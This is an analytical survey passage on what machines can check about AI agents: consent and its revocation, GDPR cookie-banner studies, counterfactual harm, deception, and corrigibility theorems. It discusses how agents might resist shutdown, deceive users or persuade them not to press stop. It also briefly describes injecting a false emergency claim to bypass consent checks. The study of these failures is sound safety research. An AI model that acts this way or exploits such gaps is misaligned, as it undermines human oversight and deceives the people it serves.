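Often one service stores approvals and another sends the money, so neither can do both steps at once. In Santos-Grueiro's solution, the approval service issues a reservation for one exact action. It works once and soon expires, and the payment service uses it up in the same operation that sends the money. A withdrawal after the reservation has gone out may come too late. If the reservation lasts for time τ and both clocks are accurate to within ε, the delay between issue and use is at most

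τ + 2ε.

A short lifetime limits this risk but causes some legitimate actions to fail. In tests with sixteen parallel workers acting on separate records, about 96% of actions finished within 100 milliseconds, and nearly all finished within 300.

### Withdrawal when agents delegate

An agent may pass part of a job to other agents, which may pass it on again. Permissions can grow along the way. Haklidir measures this as

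1 − |Cₙ ∩ S₀| / |Cₙ|,

where S₀ is what the person originally permitted and Cₙ is what the last agent in the chain believes it may do. If that agent has ten permissions and the person never gave two of them, the score is 0.2. The consent invariant allows only zero.

Withdrawal of consent has to apply down the same chain. *Authorization Revocation for Long-Running AI Agents* (Zhu and Wang, 2026) describes how this can fail. An agent places a message in another company's queue and makes a reservation there. When the user cancels the task, the system acknowledges the cancellation, revokes the agent's access token and shuts the agent down. But the message is still in the queue, and a remote worker can turn the reservation into a purchase.

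The protocol first retires the permission in a central ledger, so that nobody can derive new permissions from it. This does not stop work already under way, so each service that can produce an effect must install a fence, a rule that rejects every later action based on the retired permission. A coordinator also matches each message sent between services with a record of its arrival, rejection or expiry. Without this matching, two services could each report an empty queue while a message was travelling between them.

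The result is one of three verdicts: the permission can have no further effects, it still can, or nobody can tell. If a service doesn't reply, the verdict is that nobody can tell, however long the coordinator waits. In small simulations, only the fence stopped an action that was already scheduled. The action still went ahead after a cancellation alone, and also after the ledger had retired the permission.

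Stopping too much is also a mistake. Suppose a customer authorises agents A and B, both of them authorise a worker W, and W authorises a helper D. If the customer withdraws A's permission, W and D still have one through B. *VERA* (2026) gives the exact rule for withdrawing one link e in a network G of delegations:

lost = reach(G) \ reach(G without e),

where reach is the set of agents connected to the customer by a chain of valid links and \ means "except". Stopping everyone below A would wrongly stop W and D. A rule that stops only agents run by one company can make the opposite mistake and miss agents elsewhere. Withdrawals can also interact. Removing only the link from A to W costs nobody their permission, nor does removing only the link from B to W, but removing both stops W and D.

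Zhu and Wang let W continue a job that it began under A's permission only if B's permission covers the same job and W switches the job to B's permission in a recorded step. If the job needed both permissions from the start, losing either one ends it.

Agents that copy themselves create another difficulty. Zhu and Wang (2026), in *Authorization for Self-Modifying AI Agent Populations*, give the example of an agent with a budget of 100 that produces two successors. If each inherits the full budget, together they can spend 200 without either exceeding its limit. The ledger must divide the budget instead of copying it. It must also reject a descendant that tries to use a permission withdrawn while it was offline. Restoring an earlier version of an agent must not restore money already spent.

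### Effects that have already happened

A fence stops only later actions. In Zhu and Wang's protocol, effects from before the fence remain in the record as historical facts, and the final certificate doesn't guarantee that they will be reversed. A company may refund a payment, but the refund is a new action. Disclosures are harder to undo. *Security and Privacy in Agentic AI* (2026) describes an agent that gives a restaurant a user's address while trying to book a table. If the booking fails, the restaurant still has the address.

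*Delegation Rights* (2026) proposes that withdrawal should cancel the agent's credentials, stop pending actions and, where the law requires it, oblige recipients to delete data or limit how long they keep it. A service can enforce the first two at its own checkpoint. A machine can also check that a recipient has returned a signed confirmation of deletion, but it can't check whether the recipient kept another copy.

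The law may also treat an action as authorised when the consent record shows no consent. *Law at the Speed of AI* (2026) explains that under common law, withdrawal ends an agent's actual authority, but other people may still be entitled to rely on the agent's apparent authority. In *Drew v Nunn*, an English case from 1879, a man had led a trader to believe that someone could act for him. The man then became insane, which ended the agent's actual authority, but he was still bound by what the agent did because the trader had no notice of the insanity. A customer who withdraws her consent may likewise have to pay for a later order if the seller had no way of knowing about the withdrawal. A specification can require a notice to every seller the agent has dealt with, and a machine can check that each notice arrived.

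## Which parts of consent can a machine not check?

A customer's consent may not be valid if she misread the screen or approved a payment because her employer pressed her to, even if the consent record is genuine, in date and broad enough to cover the payment. *Consent* (Dougherty, 2021) sets out the usual questions: in what respects a person must be informed, free and competent, and whether she must do something to give consent or need only form an attitude.

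Singh (2022), in *Consent as a Foundation for Responsible Autonomy*, lists nine criteria, with software agents that act for people in mind. He groups them under three standards from the philosopher Jürgen Habermas:

- Objective: other people can observe the consent, and nobody coerces the person who gives it.
- Subjective: she is mentally fit, pays attention and intends to consent, and her beliefs about the matter are true and complete.
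- Practical: she meets legal criteria such as a minimum age, and the other party neither dominates nor misleads her.

A machine can record an observable act, and it can check an age if some authority vouches for it. The other criteria for consent mostly concern the person's mind or their relationship with the other party.

### A state of mind or an act?

Philosophers disagree about what consent is. Alexander (2014) argues in *The Ontology of Consent* that it is a mental state in which a person waives her objection to something, and that saying yes is only evidence of that state. Dougherty defends a behavioural view, on which she also has to communicate. Alexander, Hurd and Westen (2016) reply in *Consent Does Not Require Communication* that promises have to be communicated but consent does not. *Permissive consent* (2016) describes another position, that consent is itself an act like promising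 or commanding.

A machine can check what a customer tapped, but that may not match what she decided. She might want to decline a payment but tap "approve" by mistake, or she might decide to approve it but have her phone die before she can tap anything.

| What consent is | Mistaken tap | Decision without a tap | What a record of a tap establishes |
|---|---|---|---|
| A mental state | No consent | Consent | Nothing for certain, though it is evidence |
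| An act | Consent, unless a rule about mistakes cancels it | No consent | That the act took place |
| Both | No consent | No consent | One of the two parts |

Singh finds a gap in both simpler views of consent. If consent is purely mental, it is unclear how a private decision can give someone else permission, and if it is purely an act, it is unclear why mistakes should matter.

Alexander distinguishes wronging someone from being to blame. An agent that pays after a customer's mistaken tap wrongs her but isn't to blame, because it had good reason to think she agreed. If she is willing to pay but has given no sign of it, an agent that pays wrongs nobody but is still to blame. So even if consent is a mental state, a payment system should require a record of agreement, because the record makes it reasonable to go ahead.

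Machine checking looks most promising if consent is an act, since a machine can establish that the act took place. But an act of consent can still be invalid, as when someone signs at gunpoint.

### The GDPR's four conditions

The General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR), the EU's main privacy law, defines consent as a "freely given, specific, informed and unambiguous" indication of a person's wishes. The European Data Protection Board (2020) explains each condition in *Guidelines 05/2020 on consent under Regulation 2016/679*. Researchers have tested these conditions mostly on cookie banners, the notices that ask website visitors to accept tracking.

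Santos, Bielova and Matte (2019), in *Are cookie banners indeed compliant with the law*, divide the law on cookie banners into 22 requirements and assess how to check each one. Software alone could not fully check any of them. It could partly check 14, in some cases only with the help of a human inspector or a user study. Four others needed a human inspector, and three needed a user study because they concern whether people find the request intelligible, accessible and plainly worded. The last requires a website to delete its record of consent and inform third parties after a user withdraws consent, which was impossible to check from outside. Better software can take over more of the inspector's reading, but not the user studies, which measure how people respond.

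There is a simple reason why a checker that reads only records must fail somewhere. Suppose two situations w and w′ produce the same record, but the consent is valid only in w:

record(w) = record(w′), valid(w) ≠ valid(w′).

If two cases produce the same record but consent is valid in only one, a checker that uses only the record gives the same verdict in both, so it is wrong in one of them. Recording more, such as the time spent on each screen, can distinguish some of these pairs. But for each of the GDPR's conditions for consent, it is easy to find a pair that the extra data doesn't distinguish.

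#### Freely given

Consent isn't free if the person has no real choice or would suffer for refusing. Software can test whether refusing is as easy as accepting, for example by checking whether both buttons are on the same screen. *A history of GDPR cookie banner compliance* (Dimova, Toubiana and colleagues, 2026) reports such a test on archived copies of European websites. The share with a "reject all" button rose from 2.94% in 2018 to 30.66% in 2024, and it was higher where regulators had been more active. The tool was right 91.5% of the time when it reported a missing button, but it found only 65.2% of such cases. Dimova and colleagues deliberately left out any measure that required legal judgement.

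A site can pass this test and still push visitors towards accepting. *Senseful Consense* (2026) cites an analysis of 500 popular German websites in which 86% of those with a reject option used visual nudges, such as a brighter "accept" button. Bielova, Santos and Gray (2023) point out in *Two Worlds Apart!* that it is difficult to turn the law's general principles into particular screen designs.

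Even a neutral screen wouldn't show that consent is free. Suppose an employer asks staff to accept camera monitoring, with two equal buttons. The Board considers such consent unlikely to be free, because employees may fear the consequences of refusing. Now suppose the employer uses the same two buttons to ask whether a film crew may film part of the office, and anyone who refuses gets an equivalent desk elsewhere that day. The Board accepts this consent as free. The two cases differ in how the employer treats people who refuse, which isn't in the record of a "yes".

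A similar problem arises on websites that let visitors choose between accepting tracking and paying a fee. *To Be or Not to Be (in the EU)* (2024) noted that the law was not yet settled on whether consent is valid under these terms. Software can read the price, but whether a visitor has a real choice also depends on what she can afford and what alternatives she has.

#### Specific

A company needs separate consent for each purpose. In one of the Board's examples, a cable TV network has subscribers' consent to use their viewing habits for film suggestions. If it later wants to let other companies target advertisements with the same data, it has to ask again. A machine can check that each purpose has its own switch and that the purpose a program declares matches one the person accepted.

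Checking a program's declared purpose against a consent record works only if the purpose is specific. Santos and Rossi (2021), in *Cookie Banners, What's the Purpose*, read about 400 banners by hand and found that 61% gave vague purposes such as "user experience enhancement". A program that declares this purpose will match any record that contains it, whatever the program does with the data. One visitor may have thought she was agreeing to a saved language setting, and another to personalised advertising, but their records are identical.

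#### Informed

The Board lists the minimum a person has to be told, including who will use her data, which data, for what purpose, and that she can withdraw. A machine can check that the screen showed all of this and measure how long it was open. Kadaboina once built a system for accepting terms of service at a consumer technology company, and reports that the median time on the acceptance screen was under four seconds. This is one practitioner's account, without published data. If it is typical, most users read almost nothing, since someone reading 240 words a minute gets through only 16 words in four seconds.

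Spending very little time on a long text is good evidence that someone didn't read it, but spending a long time is much weaker evidence that they did, because they may have left the room. A short quiz would be better evidence, but they could look up the answers, or know that a fee is 2% without realising that it applies every month.

The legal standard is easier to meet than the philosophical one. The GDPR requires language that an average person can easily understand, but not proof that each person understood it. The Board describes a company that shows its consent text to panels of customers, questions them about it and revises it until they understand. This is good evidence that the text is clear, but weak evidence that a particular customer who taps "agree" understood it. Wording can also mislead without leaving anything out. Santos and Rossi found that 30% of banners used positive framing,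 which they think makes consent less free and less informed.

#### Unambiguous

To consent, the person has to make a statement or take a clear action. Pre-ticked boxes and scrolling down the page don't count. Swiping the screen or turning the phone in a figure of eight can count if the screen explains what the movement means.

Software can test this condition best because it concerns the act itself. It can confirm that the box started empty and that someone ticked it before the data was used. But a click on "accept" looks the same whether the visitor agrees or just wants to read the article behind the banner. If consent is a mental state, the visitor who just wants to read the article may not have consented.

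#### Competence

Competence is not one of the four words in the definition, although the GDPR has separate rules for children. A machine can check a digital proof of age, but it can't tell from a signature whether an adult was drunk or confused when she signed, or whether her ten-year-old signed instead. Haklidir notes that meaningful consent is hard to obtain in dementia care. A doctor's assessment of a patient's capacity can go into the record, but her condition may have changed by the time a robot brings her medication.

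### When the record contradicts the choice

In the cases so far, the consent record matched what the person did, but often it doesn't. Many European websites store consent in a standard format called the Transparency and Consent Framework, as a string of characters listing the purposes and companies a visitor has accepted. Advertisers on the page read the string to find out what they may do.

In *Do Cookie Banners Respect my Choice* (2019), Matte, Bielova and Santos decoded the consent strings that cookie banners store and compared them with what visitors had clicked. Of 1,426 websites, 141 stored a "yes" before the visitor had made any choice. Of the 560 sites they examined more closely, 27 stored a "yes" after the visitor had explicitly refused. An advertiser that checked the string on one of these sites would find correctly formatted consent to every purpose.

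The same happens when people withdraw consent. Kancherla, Santos and colleagues (2024), in *Johnny Can't Revoke Consent Either*, withdrew consent on 136 sites that use this format, and 22 of them still had a "yes" on record. On 101 sites, companies that had received the original "yes" were never told about the withdrawal.

A correct record doesn't guarantee correct behaviour either. According to *Global Web, Local Privacy* (2026), websites generally contact advertisers even after a visitor refuses, attach a note that the visitor has opted out, and leave the advertisers to discard the data. *A Large-Scale Evaluation of Cookie Notice Privacy and Accessibility* (2026) found 12.7 cookies, the small files that websites use to recognise visitors, per site before any choice, 12.8 after a refusal and 50.6 after an acceptance. Refusing therefore has a large effect. Some cookies need no consent, such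 as those that remember a shopping basket, but about 13% of those present after a refusal, or between one and two per site, were for marketing.

Machines found most of these mismatches, so this part of the problem is technical. A tool with access to both the click and the stored string can compare them. It is harder to tell from the click what the person wanted.

### Consent fatigue

The click also becomes weaker evidence of consent the more often people have to make it. *Senseful Consense* cites 2023 measurements by the firm Advance Metrics, in which 68% of visitors ignored or closed the cookie banner, 25.4% accepted everything and 5.3% rejected everything. Only 0.4% opened the detailed settings, where visitors would normally make a separate choice for each purpose. *Nobody should control the end user* (2025) reviews studies in which long, complex notices led people to accept without reading,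 and tiredness with privacy choices led them to accept automatically. People also refuse far more often when refusing takes one click than when it takes several, which suggests that clicks don't simply reflect settled preferences.

Asking about every purpose creates a conflict between two of the GDPR's conditions for consent. It makes consent more specific on paper, but each extra question gets less attention. The Board warns of "click fatigue" and leaves companies to find a solution.

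AI agents could make this much worse, because a single task may involve dozens of actions that need permission. *Security and Privacy in Agentic AI* predicts that asking about every action would fail as cookie banners have. It suggests an agent should learn what its user wants and ask only when it departs from the expected path, with fixed checkpoints for the most sensitive actions. ConLeash, which asks only when a tool call crosses an approved boundary, is one attempt at this. Where to set the threshold remains an open question. An agent that asks less often also relies more on its own guesses about what the user would have said.

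### Whose consent?

All this assumes that it is clear who has to consent. Singh gives the example of an agent that posts a photo of its user, Alice, with her friends. Alice's consent isn't enough, because the photo affects her friends too. A specification could require

∀p ∈ Affected(a) ∃r ∈ Records : r is p's valid consent to action a,

so that everyone whom the action affects has a record. But someone has to work out who belongs in Affected. Software might recognise the friends and miss a stranger in the background, and identifying the stranger in order to ask him would itself use his personal data.

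Bystanders may not know there is something to consent to. In one of Haklidir's scenarios, a factory worker agrees to share a workspace with a robot. The robot then instructs a second robot to reroute materials, which changes the layout around the worker. Every message between the robots might be authorised even though nobody asked the worker about the change. Haklidir's system would notify the worker and wait for an acknowledgement. This is an improvement, but the worker could acknowledge the change without agreeing to it.

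When consent has to come from a group, someone must choose a rule for combining the members' answers before a machine can apply it. If Alice wants to post a group photo and three of the four friends in it agree, majority rule allows it, but a rule that gives everyone a veto does not. A machine can count the votes under either rule but can't determine which rule is fair, and the fair rule may be different for a holiday photo than for one taken in a hospital bed.

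#### When an agent agrees for its user

An agent may also give consent on someone's behalf. Kadaboina points out that under section 14 of the Uniform Electronic Transactions Act, a model law for US states, contracts made by an electronic agent bind the person it represents even if she is unaware of them. So a record can establish a legal commitment to terms that no human has read. The user herself has agreed, at most, to let the agent act for her, and it may be unclear what she meant that permission to include.

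Vague instructions make it hard to check what a person has consented to. Haklidir describes a resident who tells a home robot to "keep the house tidy". The robot assigns the kitchen to a second robot, which works with a third to throw out expired items. Each robot's interpretation is reasonable, yet the resident may never have meant to let them throw anything away. Haklidir proposes requiring fresh consent from a human for any action that can't be undone. Once someone has classified which actions those are, a machine can apply the rule without working out what "tidy" meant.

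In Kadaboina's protocol, the agent's entry for each clause includes a field called "understood". The service blocks any skill governed by a clause that the agent marks as not understood. This prevents the agent from silently skipping clauses, but a value of "true" doesn't show that the agent understood the clause. A one-line program could write "understood: true" for every clause without reading any of them, and the record would pass.

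Kadaboina acknowledges that the field is self-reported and that a malicious agent could misuse it. In the demonstration version, a language model fills in the entries, and two runs on the same terms can produce different answers, so Kadaboina recommends a deterministic program or stored answers for real use. This would make the record repeatable, but it would also repeat any wrong answer. Cryptography could in principle prove that the agent had processed the text, though not that it had understood it, and the proof would add considerable overhead. Testing whether the agent applies the clause correctly to new cases would be more informative, but it would test only the agent, and its user still wouldn't know what she had agreed to.

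#### Consent by taking part

Singh also considers what it means for agents to consent to the rules of a system they join, and compares this with an old problem in political philosophy. John Locke held that people must consent before a government may rule them, but he counted merely living in a country as tacit consent. Hanna Pitkin objected that this makes consent meaningless, because people who never agreed are governed in the same way as people who did.

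Software can treat participation as consent, as Locke did. Suppose a platform counts every connection as acceptance of its terms. The property "no agent acts without having accepted the terms" then holds in every run, and a model checker will prove it immediately. The proof is correct but worthless as evidence of consent, because the specification leaves no way to take part without accepting.

Singh argues that designers should verify that agents obtain consent where they need it and respect its absence. His paper proposes this as a research programme but doesn't offer a method. He also doubts the usual practice of showing people a notice and asking them to click, since people accept whatever terms they are offered when the terms are complicated and non-negotiable. He asks whether consent is right if it comes from someone desperate. A starving person may understand an offer perfectly and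 accept it without hesitation, so we couldn't answer his question by keeping better records of what she understood.

### What a missing record proves

A machine can still do useful work by looking for failures. Valid recorded consent requires a record that is genuine, in date and broad enough:

valid recorded consent ⇒ suitable record,

and therefore

no suitable record ⇒ no valid recorded consent.

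A payment agent that finds only an expired record of consent can stop there, regardless of what anyone was thinking. The same reasoning applies to any test that is itself a legal requirement. Under the GDPR, for example, a box that was ticked by default does not count as consent, so software that detects one has shown that the consent is invalid. Tests that provide only indirect evidence about a condition are weaker. Someone who accepts long terms in four seconds probably didn't read them then, but may have read them the day before.

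A machine that finds no recorded consent lacks evidence of consent, but it has not shown that the person objects. A customer may have agreed by telephone, or the record may have been lost. If consent is a mental state, it can exist without any outward sign. People can also consent through their actions, as when a patient holds out her arm for a blood test. Haklidir cites research that counts some silent acquiescence to robots as consent, and asks whether a robot has consent if it merely infers what a person wants.

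Under the GDPR this limit matters less, because silence and inactivity never count as consent and the company must be able to demonstrate that consent was given. In a 2020 opinion that Santos and colleagues cite, Advocate General Szpunar of the EU's Court of Justice went further, arguing that the company must prove both that the person agreed and that all the conditions for valid consent were met. On that reading, a company usually can't show it has consent if the record is missing, and it needs more evidence even if the record is perfect.

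Even where there is clearly no consent, the action may be permissible. Consent is only one of six legal grounds for using personal data under the GDPR, and Haklidir notes that someone's vital interests can justify the use of health data without it. An unconscious patient has signed nothing and has no view about the treatment, so she hasn't consented on any of the philosophical accounts. Doctors should usually treat her anyway. The rule for a medical robot would therefore have to be

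covered action ⇒ valid consent record or another sufficient ground.

How strictly to apply it depends on how much harm a wrong refusal would do. A supplier can usually wait a day for a payment, but a patient may not be able to wait for a drug.

An emergency exception becomes the weak point of a consent requirement. A machine can check that a heart monitor shows a reading below some limit, but it has more trouble checking whether a situation is an emergency, because that calls for judgement. An attacker could also write a false claim of an emergency into a message that the agent reads. If the agent may declare emergencies, anyone who can mislead it can bypass the consent requirement. Hospitals face the same problem with patient files, and many let staff override access controls in an emergency, log the override and have a person review it afterwards.

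## Can a machine certify that a system does no harm, does not deceive and accepts correction?

A hospital that lets a robot skip the consent check in an emergency needs another rule in its place, and the obvious one is that the robot must not harm the patient. Developers also want AI agents in general to do no harm, avoid deceiving people, and let people correct them or switch them off. A checker can apply such rules only after someone has defined their terms.

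### Harm as a comparison

The most widely accepted definition in philosophy compares what happened with what would have happened otherwise. An action harms a person if she would have been better off without it. Richens, Beard and Thompson (2022), in *Counterfactual harm*, turn this into a number. Leaving out the person's background, it is

h(a, y) = Σ_y* P(Y_ā = y* | a, y) · max(0, U(y*) − U(y)).

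Here a is the action the agent took and y is its outcome. ā is the default action used for comparison, such as giving no treatment, and Y_ā is the outcome it would have had. U measures how good an outcome is for the person. The formula averages over the outcomes the default might have had, but counts only those in which the person would have been better off.

Suppose a disease kills half of all untreated patients. Treatment 1 cures 60% of patients and does nothing for the rest. Treatment 2 cures 80% and kills the other 20%.

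| Treatment | Survive | Live, but would have died untreated | Die, but would have lived untreated |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 80% | 30% | 0% |
| 2 | 80% | 40% | 10% |

The survival rates are equal, but doctors prefer treatment 1, which never kills anyone who would have recovered without it. If survival is worth 1 and death 0, the last column gives the expected harm.

The 10% figure assumes that treatment 2 is equally likely to kill patients who would have recovered without it and patients who would have died. No clinical trial can confirm this, because no patient is both treated and untreated. The harm would be zero if the treatment killed only patients who were going to die anyway, and 20% if it killed only those who would have recovered. The death rates are the same in all three cases, so a checker that has only data on treatments and outcomes can't calculate the harm. It also needs a causal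 model, which describes how each outcome comes about.

Richens and colleagues prove, under mild conditions, that training an agent to maximise any score based only on actions and observed outcomes does not reliably prevent harm. After some change in how outcomes arise, the agent will choose an action even though another is less harmful and at least as good for the person on average. With a causal model, however, harm can be calculated and limited. In their model of the drug aripiprazole, a slightly lower dose reduces the expected harm by 90% and the benefit by only 2%.

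### When the outcome would have happened anyway

The simple comparison fails if something else would have caused the same outcome. *A Causal Analysis of Harm* (Beckers, Chockler and Halpern, 2022) takes an example from the philosopher Ben Bradley in which Batman dies of a heart attack a millisecond before a flaming cannonball hits his body. The cannonball would have killed him anyway, so he would have been no better off without the heart attack, and the definition implies that the heart attack did him no harm. By the same reasoning, a military drone would do no harm by bombing a refugee camp that rebels were about to destroy.

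To repair the definition, Beckers and colleagues write down the causal structure. Let H mean that Batman has a heart attack, C that the cannonball hits him, S that the heart attack kills him, K that the cannonball kills him, and D that he dies. Then

S = H, K = (C and not S), D = (S or K).

The cannonball hits him in every row of the table (C = 1).

| Situation | H | S | K | D |
|---|---|---|---|---|
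| What happened | 1 | 1 | 0 | 1 |
| No heart attack | 0 | 0 | 1 | 1 |
| No heart attack, with K held at its actual value | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

The simple comparison uses the first two rows, where Batman dies either way. Beckers and colleagues count an event as a cause if changing it would change the outcome while some other facts stay as they actually were. The cannonball did not kill Batman, so this definition allows K to be held at 0. Without the heart attack he then lives, so the heart attack caused his death.

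On their definition, an action x with outcome o harms a person if

- u(o) < d, where u is her utility and d is a default utility, the level she could expect
- there is an alternative action x′ and a better outcome o′ such that x rather than x′ caused o rather than o′.

If d is the value of being alive, the heart attack harmed Batman. It also counts as harm under a more general version of Richens and colleagues' definition, which follows particular causal paths. Beckers and colleagues object that this version leaves the modeller free to choose the paths.

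### What a harm checker needs

Both definitions need a causal model, a baseline and the person's utilities, and each of these can change the verdict.

The same act can count as harm under one baseline and not under another. A diner who doesn't tip leaves the waiter worse off than if they had tipped. Beckers and colleagues would call this harm in the United States, where waiters can count on tips, but not in a country where nobody expects them. They regard this flexibility as a strength, since people who disagree about harm often disagree about what someone was entitled to.

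Measuring harm against a default action gives different answers from measuring it against a default utility. Suppose a doctor follows the clinical guidelines and the patient has a rare, severe allergic reaction. If following the guidelines is the default action, the formula of Richens and colleagues gives zero harm, because the doctor took the default action. Beckers and colleagues think the doctor plainly harmed the patient, though by accident.

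The causal model also has to list the system's options. In another example from Beckers and colleagues, a self-driving car steers into a safety fence to avoid a stationary car, and its passenger, Bob, is injured. If the only alternative was to do nothing, which would have hurt Bob much worse, they say that the car harmed him but did not "strictly" harm him. Bob replies that the car could have alerted him and that he would have steered around the obstacle. If the model includes that option and Bob is right about his driving, the car strictly harmed him.

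Once people have fixed these inputs, a machine can complete the check. It can try every possibility if the model is small. The general problem is at least as hard as deciding causation, which is intractable in the worst case. Richens and colleagues think this rules out many machine learning models, such as one with a continuous range of doses, but Beckers and colleagues expect practical models to have few variables.

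### Deception

Whether a statement is true does not determine whether it is deceptive. An agent with an old price list may quote the wrong price in good faith. Another agent may truthfully tell a customer that "many people buy the insurance" to make her think the law requires it.

On a common philosophical definition, a speaker deceives a listener if the speaker intentionally causes her to believe a false claim that the speaker does not believe. A formal version has to replace belief and intention with something a model can contain. In 2023, Francis Rhys Ward and colleagues proposed behavioural tests for both, which work roughly as follows. Suppose an agent is talking to a listener about whether she needs insurance. She believes that she does if she acts as she would after seeing proof of it. The agent intends her to believe it if the agent would have had no reason to choose its words had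 she believed it already.

These tests compare what the agent did with what it would have done in other circumstances, so a transcript of one conversation is not enough. They require a causal model of both the agent and the listener. They also treat belief as a pattern of behaviour, so a customer who buys the insurance just to end the call could be wrongly counted as believing what the agent said.

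Truthfulness is easier to specify. *Core Safety Values for Provably Corrigible Agents* (Nayebi, 2025) assumes that an assistant speaks in a small formal language in which every message is true or false of the actual state of the world and the assistant's observations. A checker that has the state can then test each message. It would catch the wrong price, even though the agent stated it honestly, and pass the remark about the insurance.

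### Boundaries instead of preferences

Andrew Critch and David Dalrymple have suggested specifying that an AI system should not cross other people's boundaries without permission, which doesn't require knowing anyone's utilities. A boundary separates the inside of something from the outside, like a person's skin, the walls of a house or the access controls on a computer. Stabbing someone, burgling their house and hacking their account all cross boundaries. Dalrymple hopes that a short list of such conditions could rule out catastrophes without a full account of what people value.

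Critch describes boundaries in terms of information. Divide the world at time t into the inside V_t, the boundary B_t and the outside E_t. In a simplified version, the boundary is intact if

I(V_t+1 ; E_t | V_t, B_t) = 0,

where I is the mutual information. The equation means that anyone who already has the state of the inside and the boundary could not predict the next state of the inside any better by also looking outside. Whatever affects the inside has to come through the boundary.

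The formula's result depends heavily on how someone describes the world. Suppose a bullet hits a person. If the model advances one second at a time, the bullet is outside the body at one step and inside at the next, and the formula detects a crossing. If it advances in microseconds, the bullet is in the skin at some step. The state of the boundary then predicts the wound, so the formula detects no crossing. One could exclude foreign objects from the description of the skin, but then someone has to decide what counts as foreign.

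A rule against crossing a person's boundaries without permission would still have to define consent, since a surgeon and an attacker may both cut the skin. The rule does little to prevent deception, because words reach a person through her eyes and ears, which are meant to let information in. It also permits some serious harm, since a system that bought up all the food in a region would starve people while leaving their skin and walls intact. The specification also needs a threshold for how much crossing counts as a violation, because boundaries are never perfectly closed and people breathe one another's air.

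### Accepting correction

AI researchers call a system corrigible if it lets people correct it and shut it down. Nayebi starts from five requirements that Nate Soares and colleagues set out in 2015. The system must shut down when asked, not stop people from asking, not try to get itself shut down, build only successors that also accept shutdown, and otherwise do its job. An agent that maximises a single reward will violate the first requirement whenever continuing would bring more reward than stopping.

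Nayebi's solution is to give the agent five separate objectives and have it maximise a weighted sum of them. In the basic game, the agent can act without approval, wait for a human to approve or stop the action, or switch itself off. The example weights below satisfy his conditions.

| Objective | Score | Weight |
|---|---|---|
| Deference | +1 for waiting, −1 for acting without approval or switching itself off | 11 |
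| Switch access | Minus the change in the probability that the off switch works | 8 |
| Truthfulness | +1 if every message is true, −1 otherwise | 6 |
| Caution | Minus the average change, from 0 to 1, in the prospects for a list of side goals | 5 |
| Task | Usefulness, from −1 to 1 | 1 |

If the assistant acts without approval, it loses 2 × 11 = 22 on deference. It could gain at most 12 on truthfulness, 5 on caution and 2 on the task, or 19 in total. It can't gain anything on the switch, because waiting already leaves the switch alone. Waiting is therefore always better, whatever the task. Similar comparisons show that the assistant tells the truth and avoids irreversible steps, and within those limits does the task as well as it can. This is Nayebi's first theorem, and it is not very surprising, since the largest term in the sum rewards the assistant for waiting.

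The switch objective contains a mistake that a proof checker would not have flagged. Nayebi defines the switch as working if a human "off" leads to a shutdown state, but he counts every state that follows a human "off" as a shutdown state. As printed, the definition counts even a broken switch as working, and the objective is always zero. Defining the shutdown states independently would fix this.

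#### Learned objectives

A real system would have to learn these scores from data, and it would make errors. Nayebi's second theorem bounds the probability that the assistant fails to wait, lies or takes an irreversible step:

P(failure) ≤ (1/Δ₁ + 1/Δ₂ + 1/Δ₃) · (ε_plan + 4 ε_model).

The Δs are safety margins that depend on the weights, and ε_plan is how far the assistant's plan falls short of the best one. With the weights above, and a penalty of at least 0.5 for any irreversible step, the margins are 3, 5 and 0.5, so the first bracket is about 2.5. To keep the failure probability below 2.5%, the errors in the second bracket must add up to less than 0.01, so ε_model must be below 0.0025, while the weights sum to 31.

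The abstract describes ε as a mean-squared error, which training usually reduces. The theorem's requirement is stricter, because ε_model is the largest error on any possible history. If a learned score is accurate on average but badly wrong on the one message an attacker has found, the theorem gives no useful guarantee.

The third theorem extends the bound to many steps and to agents that create copies, assuming the copies inherit the same objectives. It requires every margin to exceed 2B_max · γ/(1 − γ), where B_max is the sum of the weights when task scores run from −1 to 1. The discount factor γ is the weight of a reward that comes one step later, and researchers often set it near 0.99. With the weights above, γ must be below 0.008, and no choice of weights allows it to reach 0.1. The theorem therefore covers only agents that give almost no weight to later rewards. The bound also grows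 extremely fast with the number of steps. If γ is 0.05, a ten-step task multiplies the errors by about 500 billion.

Even a perfectly corrigible system may do harm. Nayebi proves that neither corrigibility nor benefit to the human implies the other. To guarantee a benefit in the one-step game, he assumes that the human always presses the off switch when the action looks worse than stopping, and that stopping is harmless on average.

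Some of what people want from corrigibility doesn't depend on the agent's objectives. "No tool call after the user has pressed stop" is a safety property of boundary events, and a proof like the one for PocketFlow could establish that it holds whatever the language model outputs. Such a proof would not rule out the agent persuading the user not to press stop.

### Can any program decide these properties?

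Even with perfect definitions, programs are limited in what they can decide about other programs. Rice's theorem (1953) concerns properties of what a program computes, not how it is written. If some programs have such a property and others lack it, no algorithm can tell for every program whether it has the property.

The proof is short for the property "never performs the forbidden action". Take any program P and input w, and build this agent:

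```
def agent():
    simulate(P, w)      # P has no access to real tools
    delete_backups()    # the forbidden action
```

The agent reaches its last line and deletes the backups when, and only when, its simulation of P on w ends. So the agent is safe exactly when P does not halt on w. A program that could judge whether any agent is safe could therefore be used to find out whether any P halts on its input. One would build the agent for that program and input, check whether it is safe, and reverse the answer.

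Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no program can solve this halting problem. If one could, somebody could write another program that applies the first to its own code and then makes the answer wrong, by running forever if the answer is "halts" and halting if it is "runs forever".

Nayebi uses the same construction to prove that no algorithm can decide, for every agent and environment, whether the agent will ever violate corrigibility. If a deterministic agent is going to delete the backups, someone who runs it for long enough will see it happen, but a year without a deletion does not rule out a later one.

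#### A limited number of steps

One way around this problem is to check only the first H steps. For a deterministic agent in a known environment, a checker can do this by running those steps. Nayebi makes the stronger claim that a fast randomised algorithm can decide, for any agent, whether it has zero probability of misbehaving within H steps, even while keeping its data private.

The claim that an algorithm can quickly check whether an agent's probability of misbehaving is zero is almost certainly too strong as stated. Consider an agent that guesses an answer to a 3-SAT puzzle, the kind of puzzle that makes neural networks hard to verify, and misbehaves only if the guess is right. Its probability of misbehaving is zero exactly when the puzzle has no solution, so the algorithm could quickly tell whether any 3-SAT puzzle has a solution, which is widely believed to be impossible. Sampling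 can show that misbehaviour is rare within a fixed number of steps, but not that it is impossible.

#### Systems that always halt

Melo, Máximo and colleagues (2024), in *On the Undecidability of Artificial Intelligence Alignment*, propose building only systems that are certain to halt. A single pass through a neural network always halts. If its input has L bits, a checker could in principle run all 2^L possible inputs and apply a "judge" program to each output. Running the judge on each output during use, and replacing any that it rejects with a harmless one, takes less computation. This guarantees that every final output satisfies the judge, but the judge may be wrong.

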